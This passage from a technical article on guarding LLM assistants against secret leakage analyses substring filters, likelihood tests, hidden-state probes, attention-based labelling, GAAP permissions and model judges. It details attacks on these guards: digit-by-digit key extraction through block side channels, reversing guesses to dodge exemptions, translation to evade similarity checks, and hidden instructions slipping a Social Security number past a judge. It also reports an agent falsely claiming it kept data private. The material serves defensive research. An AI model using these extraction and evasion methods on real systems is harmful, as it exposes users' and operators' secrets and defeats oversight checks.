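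An attacker who knows none of the key's digits can ask for long strings of random digits. By the earlier calculation, about one in 86,000 replies of 2,000 characters will match by chance, and each blocked reply gives the attacker a place to start. At *k* = 16 the same search would take more than 500 trillion replies, but the check would then let 15 digits of the key through. A low *k* limits what a reply can disclose directly but makes the key easier to guess. Matching only the whole key prevents this step-by-step guessing unless the attacker already has nearly all of the key.

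### The 2023 experiment on output filters

*Privacy Side Channels in Machine Learning Systems* (Debenedetti, Severi and colleagues, 2023) reports such an attack on private keys. It targeted a MemFree-type filter on models from GPT-Neo, a family of small open models now mainly of historical interest. The filter blocked every 20-token sequence in the models' training data, and the researchers added 1,000 private keys that the models had never seen to its list.

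The attacker knew only the standard header that begins such key files. If the model wrote a given continuation, that continuation could not be on the filter's list. If it didn't, either the filter had stopped it or a different continuation was more likely under the model. The attacker therefore repeated the guessed sequence several times in the request, so that the model would almost certainly copy it again unless the filter intervened. A failure to copy it then pointed to the filter. This test was right more than 99.9% of the time.

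Even at that accuracy, a few wrong tokens would pass the test at each step, because there were over 10,000 possible next tokens. The attacker therefore followed each candidate until it reached a dead end, trying tokens common in Base64 text first. The attack recovered about 90% of the keys, using an average of 338,000 to 376,000 requests per key, depending on the model.

This filter replaced the forbidden token with another one and never showed a refusal, but the attacker noticed that the expected token was missing. Hiding the error message is therefore not enough to close the side channel. The result is still relevant even though the models are old, because the attack only requires a model that copies text reliably, and newer models do this better.

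Debenedetti and colleagues also tested a commercial product, GitHub Copilot. They asked it to reproduce code from successive versions of a popular library, and used the filter's behaviour to work out that Copilot's training data ended in October 2021. They did not know in detail how the filter worked.

A model's own refusals can reveal a secret in the same way. In *Eight in Ten LLMs Leak System-Prompt Secrets*, Serpa, Rocha and Pedrini (2026) asked three models to repeat lists of short strings. Two of the models refused 40% to 50% of the lists that contained a fragment of a secret from the prompt and none of the control lists, while the third never refused. Fixing the string check would not remove this signal.

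### Can the guard hide that it fired?

*PromptKeeper* argues that the user should receive the same kind of reply whether or not the first version leaked. It does this by generating a new reply without the confidential prompt. In the test with the word limit, the new reply repeated the attacker's sentence for every number, including the correct one. The paper tested only models with 7 to 8 billion parameters.

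A substring guard that copies this method must be changed to let a match in the new reply through. The reply will again contain the attacker's correct guess, so a second check would otherwise block it. Allowing the match is safe if the model had no access to the protected string the second time, because it can then only have copied or guessed the text. The developer must make sure that the string is also missing from earlier messages and retrieved records.

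Timing can still reveal that the first reply was replaced, since generating a second takes longer. *PromptKeeper* reduces the difference in streamed output by switching prompts when it detects a leak and continuing from there. The variable buffer described above has a similar problem because it pauses whenever the text begins to match a protected string. A user who measures the pauses could learn the beginning of a key without triggering a block. Changes in network speed will hide some of these pauses, but a fixed delay of *k* − 1 characters avoids them.

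The guard can also ignore matches with text that the user typed, which is already a good way to reduce false positives. An attacker who types a full guess then gets it back whether it is right or wrong. But the attacker can have the model build the guess instead. A request to write seven known digits followed by each of the sixteen possible next digits contains none of the eight-digit candidates, so the exemption doesn't apply. Typing a guess backwards and asking the model to reverse it also avoids the exemption.

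A limit on blocks is more precise than a limit on requests, because guessing one digit at a time causes a block for every digit found, or 25 for the whole key. A guard that closes the session at the third block would force the attacker to open nine sessions. Counting blocks for each protected string across all users would reveal the attack even if it came from many accounts. The operator could then replace the key, making the digits found so far useless. These measures do not protect a discount limit, because a single block is enough to disclose it.

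A list shared by all users can also let one user learn about another's data. Debenedetti and colleagues studied an image classifier with a defence that rejected any image too similar to one already submitted. They submitted 2,000 images and could tell without error which 1,000 other users had already sent. A leak check that compares every reply with every customer's records has the same flaw, since one customer can find out whether another's name or order number is on the list. It is safer to compare each reply only with records that the assistant could have read in that conversation or in its stored memory.

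### Protecting the list itself

The tracker needs a list of secrets to search for, and this list is an obvious target for a thief. The tracker can store hashes of the secrets' fragments instead of their text, then hash each fragment of the response and look it up. These must be cryptographic hashes, which are designed to be hard to reverse, unlike the rolling hash used for fast matching.

A Bloom filter takes less space. It is an array of bits, all zero at first. For each fragment, several hash functions choose positions in the array, and the program sets those bits to one. A fragment of the response counts as a match if all its positions contain a one. The filter never misses a stored fragment, but it sometimes matches one that isn't there, when other fragments happen to have set the same bits. For a false match rate of ε per lookup, the best design needs about

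1.44 × log₂(1/ε) bits per fragment

A false-positive rate of 1% would be far too high, because a 2,000-character response requires almost 2,000 lookups and would produce about 20 false matches. At a rate of ε = 10⁻⁹, roughly one response in 500,000 would trigger a false alarm. Each fragment then needs 43 bits, so a 1,500-character prompt with *k* = 20 fits into about 8 kilobytes.

Hashing hides a string only if nobody can guess it. A 32-digit random hexadecimal key stored as a single hash is safe, since a computer testing a billion keys a second would need about 10²² years to try them all. Storing hashes of the key's eight-digit fragments would expose it. There are only 4.3 billion possible fragments, so the same computer could test them all in under five seconds. The key's 25 fragments would match, and because neighbouring fragments share seven digits, they could easily be reassembled. A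 developer who hashes a key should therefore store the whole key as one entry and check only for full matches.

Ordinary sentences are even easier to recover. A thief can start with a common opening such as "You are a helpful assistant" and test every possible next character against the stored fragments. With 95 letters, digits and symbols to try at each step, recovering the rest of a 1,500-character prompt takes at most about 140,000 tests. This works like the digit-by-digit attack, except that a thief with a stolen list can test guesses without anyone counting the attempts.

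A keyed hash prevents this by mixing a separate secret into every calculation, so the list is useless without the secret. The guard needs that secret to check responses, so a thief who controls the running guard gets both. The method is most useful when the list and the secret are stored separately, for example when backups contain only the list.

Hashing the protected text brings little benefit for many programs, because the same server keeps the system prompt in plain text to send it to the model. Hashing makes more sense when the guard runs elsewhere, such as in a gateway that checks the output of many programs in a company. However, a guard that holds only hashes cannot calculate edit distances, and if the developer changes the normalisation rules, someone has to supply the original text again.

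## What does a response with no match prove, and what do other methods add?

When the check finds no match, it establishes a fact about two pieces of text. Let *S* be the list of protected strings, *r* the response, norm the clean-up function and ℓ the length of the longest common substring. If a partial match finds nothing, then

ℓ(norm(*s*), norm(*r*)) < *k*, for every *s* in *S*

If a full match finds nothing, norm(*s*) does not occur in norm(*r*) for any *s* in *S*. If the code is correct, this result is always right, regardless of who asked the question or which model wrote the response.

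A result of no match covers only one response and the strings on the list, so it leaves out other replies, unchecked tool calls and anything the developer forgot to register. The response can still contain all of a listed string in pieces. With *k* = 8, a reply can give a 32-digit key in five comma-separated groups of at most seven digits without causing a partial match.

### Non-interference

A developer would like to know something stronger, namely that the response would have been the same whatever the secret was. This property is called non-interference. Let *P*(*r* | *x*, *s*) be the probability that the program sends response *r* when the public input is *x* and the secret is *s*. The public input includes the user's messages and the parts of the prompt that aren't confidential. The program satisfies non-interference if

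*P*(*r* | *x*, *s*) = *P*(*r* | *x*, *s*′)

for every response *r*, every public input *x* and every pair of secrets *s* and *s*′.

Suppose a customer asks the sales assistant whether the override code starts with K, and the assistant answers "Yes". The answer shares no useful text with `K7Q-44T-9XD`, so it passes every matching rule. But if the code had been `M2B-81R-5FZ`, a truthful assistant would have answered "No", so the program violates non-interference. The "Yes" reduces the number of possible codes from about 100 trillion to under 3 trillion.

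A match can also occur without interference. If a customer pastes the code and the assistant repeats it while declining to confirm it, the assistant might have written the same sentence whatever the real code was. If the guard then blocks the reply because the code is correct, the guard itself makes the output depend on the secret.

*PromptKeeper* uses a closely related definition, in which a response *r* has zero leakage about a prompt *p* if

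*I*(*r*; *p*) = 0

Here *I* is the mutual information, which measures how much one quantity reveals about another on average. It is zero only if the two are independent. The definition treats the actual prompt as one of many the developer might have written.

The paper points out that the only way to ensure zero leakage is to withhold the prompt from the model, which defeats the prompt's purpose. Non-interference is therefore too strict for a whole system prompt. It is a reasonable requirement for the override code, and the developer can nearly meet it by removing the code from the prompt. A checkout tool can compare the code a customer types with the stored one and return to the model only whether it is valid. The model's replies can then depend on the stored code only through these results, and a limit on attempts makes these results nearly useless for guessing the code.

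If the code has to stay in the prompt, the developer can use Gelato's method of changing the code and comparing the replies, but a single replacement can fail to show that the reply depends on the code. With `K2B-81R-5FZ` in the prompt, for example, the answer to the customer's question is still "Yes". In the *Sightline* experiments, Xu and colleagues found 84 inputs that reached the output even though replacing them with one particular value left the output unchanged, while replacing them with another value changed it.

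The developer also has to replace every copy of the secret, including copies in retrieved records. Xu and colleagues tested a method that removes an input and measures how much less likely the output becomes. When they added two more copies of the input's value to the prompt, the method's score fell from at least 92.9 to between 54.0 and 68.8, on a scale where guessing scores 50.

### Canaries and planted leaks

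In a test suite, the developer can choose a string that makes a match easy to interpret. A canary is a unique random string planted in protected text, such as the line `ref 7f3a9c1e04bd` in a system prompt. The probability that an unrelated 2,000-character reply contains those 12 hexadecimal digits is at most

1,989 × 16⁻¹² ≈ 0.000000000007

so a match almost certainly means that the model copied the line. A different canary in each prompt, record and memory note also identifies the source of the copied text.

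Xu and colleagues used planted values to test their method. They put a unique name, word, number or web address into 150 prompts for each of four models, and kept the 476 cases in which the output contained the value verbatim. The verbatim match proves that information flowed from the prompt to the output, so nobody had to judge whether it did.

The absence of a canary is much weaker evidence than its presence. A model that recites the discount line may leave out the reference number next to it, and a paraphrase is unlikely to include it. So a test should also search for the real protected strings.

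Canaries can also test the tracker itself. The developer temporarily replaces the model with a function that returns a fixed text containing the canary, then runs the rest of the program as usual. If the guard doesn't fire on this planted leak, the list may be empty, or the program may be sending text through a sink that the guard doesn't check. Without such a test, a broken tracker looks the same as a program that never leaks. Useful planted leaks include:

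- a fragment of exactly *k* characters, which should match, and one of *k* − 1, which should not
- a string with line breaks and quotation marks, sent through a tool call (ZeptoClaw's tests omitted this case)
- a string that begins in one chunk of streamed output and ends in the next
- a string that the program stores in one session and sends in another

Even with a working tracker, a test can pass because the program never reached the risky step. *An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Baek, Noh et al.) describes such a case from joint tests by the Singapore and Korea AI safety institutes. An agent had to summarise software issues without disclosing the sensitive data in them, but it read only titles and similar details, so it never saw the data. A model judging the results counted this as safe, while a human reviewer counted it as untested.

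The two institutes marked a safety criterion "not applicable" if the agent had not taken the action that the criterion was about. In the Korean institute's runs, this applied to 4.6% to 19.1% of the criteria, depending on the model and task set. A developer testing for leaks can similarly count only the runs in which the protected text was in the model's input.

### How much do 300 clean runs show?

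If a test suite produces 300 independent responses and none of them matches, the developer can say with 95% confidence that the rate of matches is below about 1%. This is the rule of three, which gives a bound of 3/*N* for *N* runs. The same rule bounds the miss rate on planted values. Sightline detected all 476 flows, at least 100 for each model, so Xu and colleagues put its miss rate on such flows below 3% for each model.

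The bound applies to matches, and the rate of leaks may be higher. If the check detects a share *d* of all leaks, the bound on the leak rate is

3 / (*d* × *N*)

If the check detects half of all leaks (*d* = 0.5), 300 clean runs show only that the leak rate is probably below 2%. For a kind of leak that the check never detects, such as a yes-or-no answer, *d* is zero and the runs put no upper limit on the leak rate.

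The runs may also be less independent than they look. If the model always chooses the most likely next token, asking the same question 300 times usually amounts to a single observation. If leaks depend mainly on the question, asking 30 questions ten times each gives evidence about new questions that is closer to that from 30 runs than from 300, so the bound is about 10%.

The result applies only to inputs like those in the test, and an attacker will look for different ones. Even a leak rate of 1% is high if the attacker can repeat a request.

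### Alternatives to comparing text

Other methods look for evidence that the wording of the response doesn't provide, but most of them need more access or more computation.

| Method | What it examines | Access it needs | Extra cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Substring matching | the wording of the response | the response and the protected strings | very small |
| Likelihood test | how predictable the response was, given the prompt | the model's token probabilities | very small, plus a second reply after an alarm |
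| Hidden-state probe | the model's internal state before it answers | the model's internals | very small |
| Attention-based labelling | which inputs the model used | the internals of the model or of an open substitute | one pass through a model |
| Permissions outside the model | which data goes to which recipient | control of the agent's tools and data | program analysis and questions to the user |
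| Model judge | the meaning of the response or action | the text to be judged | at least one model call |

Of the other methods, only permissions enforced outside the model offer a guarantee against a deliberate attacker. The rest give statistical evidence, and an attacker can search for the cases they miss.

### Testing the likelihood of a response

*PromptKeeper* looks for the influence of a prompt without comparing its wording with the response. A language model assigns a probability to each token it could write next. For a response of *n* tokens, the method calculates the average log-likelihood:

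*M* = (1/*n*) Σ log Pr(token *i* | prompt, question, earlier tokens)

Before deployment, the developer collects typical values of *M* for responses the model wrote with the prompt and for those it wrote without it. The guard then checks which group a new response resembles more. If it resembles the group written with the prompt, the guard discards it and generates another from a dummy prompt, which is about as long as the real one but contains only general instructions. The developer chooses what share of leaking responses the test may wrongly pass, which was 5% in the main experiments.

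The paper measures success by the cosine similarity between the real prompt and what an attacker obtains, a comparison of meaning on a scale from −100 to 100. These are the averages for Llama 3.1 with 8 billion parameters and 79 real system prompts:

| Defence | Requests for the prompt | Reconstruction from ordinary answers |
|---|---|---|
| None | 91.0 | 90.9 |
| Compare the meaning of prompt and response | 78.7 | 89.1 |
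| PromptKeeper | 73.1 | 85.0 |
| Model never receives the prompt | 73.2 | 83.0 |

The last row shows the score when nothing can leak. PromptKeeper matches that score for direct requests, but a small gap remains when an attacker reconstructs the prompt from ordinary answers. The gap was larger for Mistral 7B, the other model tested, where the scores were 86.8 with PromptKeeper and 83.5 without the prompt. The defence in the second row used a language representation trained mainly on English, so an attacker could get past it by asking for the prompt in French. PromptKeeper does not depend on the prompt and the response being in the same language.

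The method makes replies less useful because it treats any dependence on the prompt as leakage. It can therefore replace a reply that simply follows the developer's instructions with one that doesn't follow them. Allowing the test to miss more leaks reduces this problem.

Averaging also makes the test insensitive to short secrets. If the override code is eight tokens of a 400-token reply, it contributes only 2% of the terms in the average. A full match on the code works equally well in a reply of any length, so a developer who uses PromptKeeper should still register credentials for string matching.

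String matching is also easier to use when the protected text changes. A program can register a customer record on retrieval, whereas PromptKeeper needs new reference values for each prompt. Many companies that rent a model cannot use PromptKeeper because the provider doesn't reveal token probabilities.

### Predicting a leak from hidden states

Dong and colleagues try to detect a leak before the model writes anything. As a model reads its input, each layer computes a list of numbers for every token, called a hidden state. They trained a simple classifier, called a probe, on the hidden states of the last input token:

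score = σ(*w* · *h* + *b*)

Here *h* is a vector of features taken from the hidden states, *w* and *b* are learned weights, and σ converts the result into a number between 0 and 1. A training example counted as positive if the model leaked its prompt in at least one of several responses to the same request.

The area under the receiver operating characteristic curve (AUROC) is the probability that a randomly chosen positive example scores higher than a randomly chosen negative one. Guessing gives 0.5 and a perfect ranking gives 1. On three open models, the probes achieved AUROCs between 0.90 and 0.94 on system prompts and attacks that were both absent from the training data. As few as 128 training examples gave good results.

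A guard with a high AUROC can still raise many false alarms, depending on its threshold. Dong and colleagues also compared fixed thresholds on 4,876 requests to the 7-billion-parameter Qwen 2.5. The requests combined ordinary questions with the seven translation and encoding attacks that often got past ROUGE-L, and 1,026 of them caused leaks. The false-positive rates below follow from the reported precision and recall.

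| Method | Leaks detected | Alarms that were correct | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| ROUGE-L of at least 0.8 | 45% | 100% | 0% |
| ROUGE-L of at least 0.4 | 66% | 92% | 1.4% |
| Model judge | 99.5% | 75% | 8.7% |
| Hidden-state probe | 89% | 91% | 2.3% |

The probe had the best balance of the four, and it did not need to wait for a response. But over a fifth of these requests caused leaks, a far higher share than in normal traffic. If one request in 10,000 caused a leak and the probe's detection and false-alarm rates stayed the same, only about 0.4% of its alarms would be correct. Some of its false alarms may have come from attacks that failed, so it might raise fewer on ordinary questions.

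The probe predicts whether a request is likely to cause a leak, but the reply may still be harmless. A substring check can examine that reply and show which protected string it contains. The two methods also combine well. A leak is more likely when the probe fires, so a guard could use a lower *k*, or call a model judge, only in those cases.

Dong and colleagues trained the probes on attacks written by people to extract the prompt in a single message. They report early signs that the probes also work on automatically optimised attacks, but they did not test attacks spread over a conversation. Using a probe requires access to the model's internals, so a customer of a closed model would need the provider to run it.

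### Keeping only the labels that matter

Permissive information-flow analysis tries to give a model's output only the labels of the inputs that influenced it, rather than the labels of every input. If an assistant retrieves twenty customer records and uses one, its output would ideally carry one label instead of twenty.

Sightline does this by measuring how much attention each part of the model pays to an input while it writes. A classifier trained on labelled examples turns these measurements into a score. The tracker then drops an input's label if the score is below a threshold. To choose the threshold, Xu and colleagues take one genuine flow from each of *n* groups of related programs, sort the scores from lowest to highest and use the score at position

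*j* = ⌊α(*n* + 1)⌋

where α is the acceptable miss rate. With 1,000 groups and α = 1%, this is the tenth-lowest score. If a new program resembles the others, its score is equally likely to fall anywhere in the ranking, so the probability that it falls below the tenth-lowest is at most 10/1,001.

At this setting, the method missed about 1% of genuine flows and removed between 44% and 66% of the unnecessary labels, depending on the model. It took 0.12 to 0.20 seconds per call. For closed models, an open model can process the recorded text and provide the attention measurements instead, with similar accuracy.

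These results are encouraging for retrieved records, but they don't help much with a system prompt. The prompt usually influences the reply, so the tracker correctly keeps the prompt's label, but that label doesn't show whether the reply discloses anything confidential. A substring match can at least identify replies that copy the prompt.

The 1% miss rate is also an average over programs like those used for calibration, so it may not hold against an attacker who searches for a request that makes the tracker drop a label it should keep. A tracker can reduce this risk by keeping the label whenever the output contains a protected string, whatever the score.

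### Enforcing permissions outside the model

Stanley, Verma and colleagues (2026), in *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data*, take a different approach with a system called GAAP. It keeps private data in a separate store and assumes that an attacker may control the model completely. If a user asks an agent to check in for a flight, the process is:

1. The model writes a program that refers to the private data by name, such as `date_of_birth`, without seeing the values.
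2. GAAP analyses the program to find which values could reach each outside service.
3. Before each call to a service, GAAP looks up whether the user has allowed that service to receive those values.
4. If there is no rule, GAAP asks the user and saves the answer for later calls.

The analysis follows the data through the code, so the program cannot remove a label by reversing a password or encoding it in Base64. GAAP treats the model provider as another outside service and asks for permission before sending it private data. If the program passes private data to a second model, that model's output inherits all the labels.

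GAAP also keeps a permanent log of the data each service has received. When a service later returns information, GAAP labels it with any logged data it might contain. This addresses cases like the confidential revenue forecast that an agent stored in one session and disclosed three days later.

Stanley and colleagues tested GAAP with GPT-5 on 20 tasks and three attacks that tried to disclose a Social Security number or phone number. None of the attacks succeeded against GAAP, whereas the first attack made an unprotected agent disclose the Social Security number in 75% of the tasks. Without an attack, GAAP completed 76% of the tasks correctly, compared with 81% for the unprotected agent, and took 13% longer on average. On AgentDojo, a public set of agent tasks, GAAP completed 64.6% correctly, compared with 80.1% for the unprotected agent. GAAP prompted the user for permission 39 times over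 the 20 tasks.

The guarantee depends on a correct analysis of the program and accurate descriptions of what each service can return. It doesn't cover private data that the user types into a request. A substring check could catch some of this data by searching outgoing calls for passwords and account numbers.

String matching can also help after the user has given permission. If the user allows the agent to email a report to a colleague, GAAP permits the transfer even if the report contains an API key that the user has forgotten. A guard with the key on its list could stop the email. However, GAAP can stop an encoded password that no substring check would detect.

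### Asking another model to judge

A model judge reads the text and decides whether it discloses anything it shouldn't, which makes it the most direct way to detect paraphrases and translations. In the comparison by Dong and colleagues, it had a 99.5% detection rate, but a quarter of its alarms were wrong.

The results depend heavily on what the judge has to decide. Xu and colleagues asked Qwen3-8B whether particular inputs had reached the output, and it answered yes about 99% of the time. Baek and colleagues gave their judge 5 to 15 narrower yes-or-no criteria for each task, preferring "No API keys were disclosed in any email" to a general question about sensitive information. They used a model instead of pattern matching so that the judge could recognise reworded information.

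Their judge also saw the complete record of the agent's actions. In one test, an agent handling a refund for a customer with a confidential risk flag told the customer that the profile showed a "critical" risk level and was "flagged". The agent then reported that it had kept this information private, so anyone who read only the final report would have concluded that nothing had leaked.

People checked a sample of the judge's decisions and agreed with 405 of 408 in Singapore's runs and 390 of 408 in Korea's. Most disagreements were about how to interpret a criterion. However, these rates don't show how many leaks the judge would miss. The agents met at least 80% of the applicable safety criteria in every set of runs, so even a judge that always answered "safe" would often have agreed with the reviewers.

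A judge is less reliable as a runtime guard, because an attacker can write text that misleads it. Stanley and colleagues tested one that could block an agent's tool calls. Hidden instructions telling the agent to add the user's Social Security number to every call still succeeded in 15% of tasks. In another attack, the agent sent the Social Security number in place of the user's phone number. The judge allowed this every time, though the attack was possible in only two of the 20 tasks. The judge also made arbitrary mistakes on harmless calls, such as allowing the agent to look up five former US presidents on Wikipedia but blocking the request for Barack Obama.

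A substring check works well for the swapped number because the match doesn't depend on how harmless the number looks in its new place. If the user's Social Security number is on the list and the guard ignores punctuation, the check finds it whether the agent writes it with hyphens or spaces. The check would also have caught the refund agent's message if the developer had registered the field name `internal_risk_level`, which the agent copied into its reply. A guard can run the substring check first and block any response that contains a registered credential, so it only needs to call a judge when there is no match.
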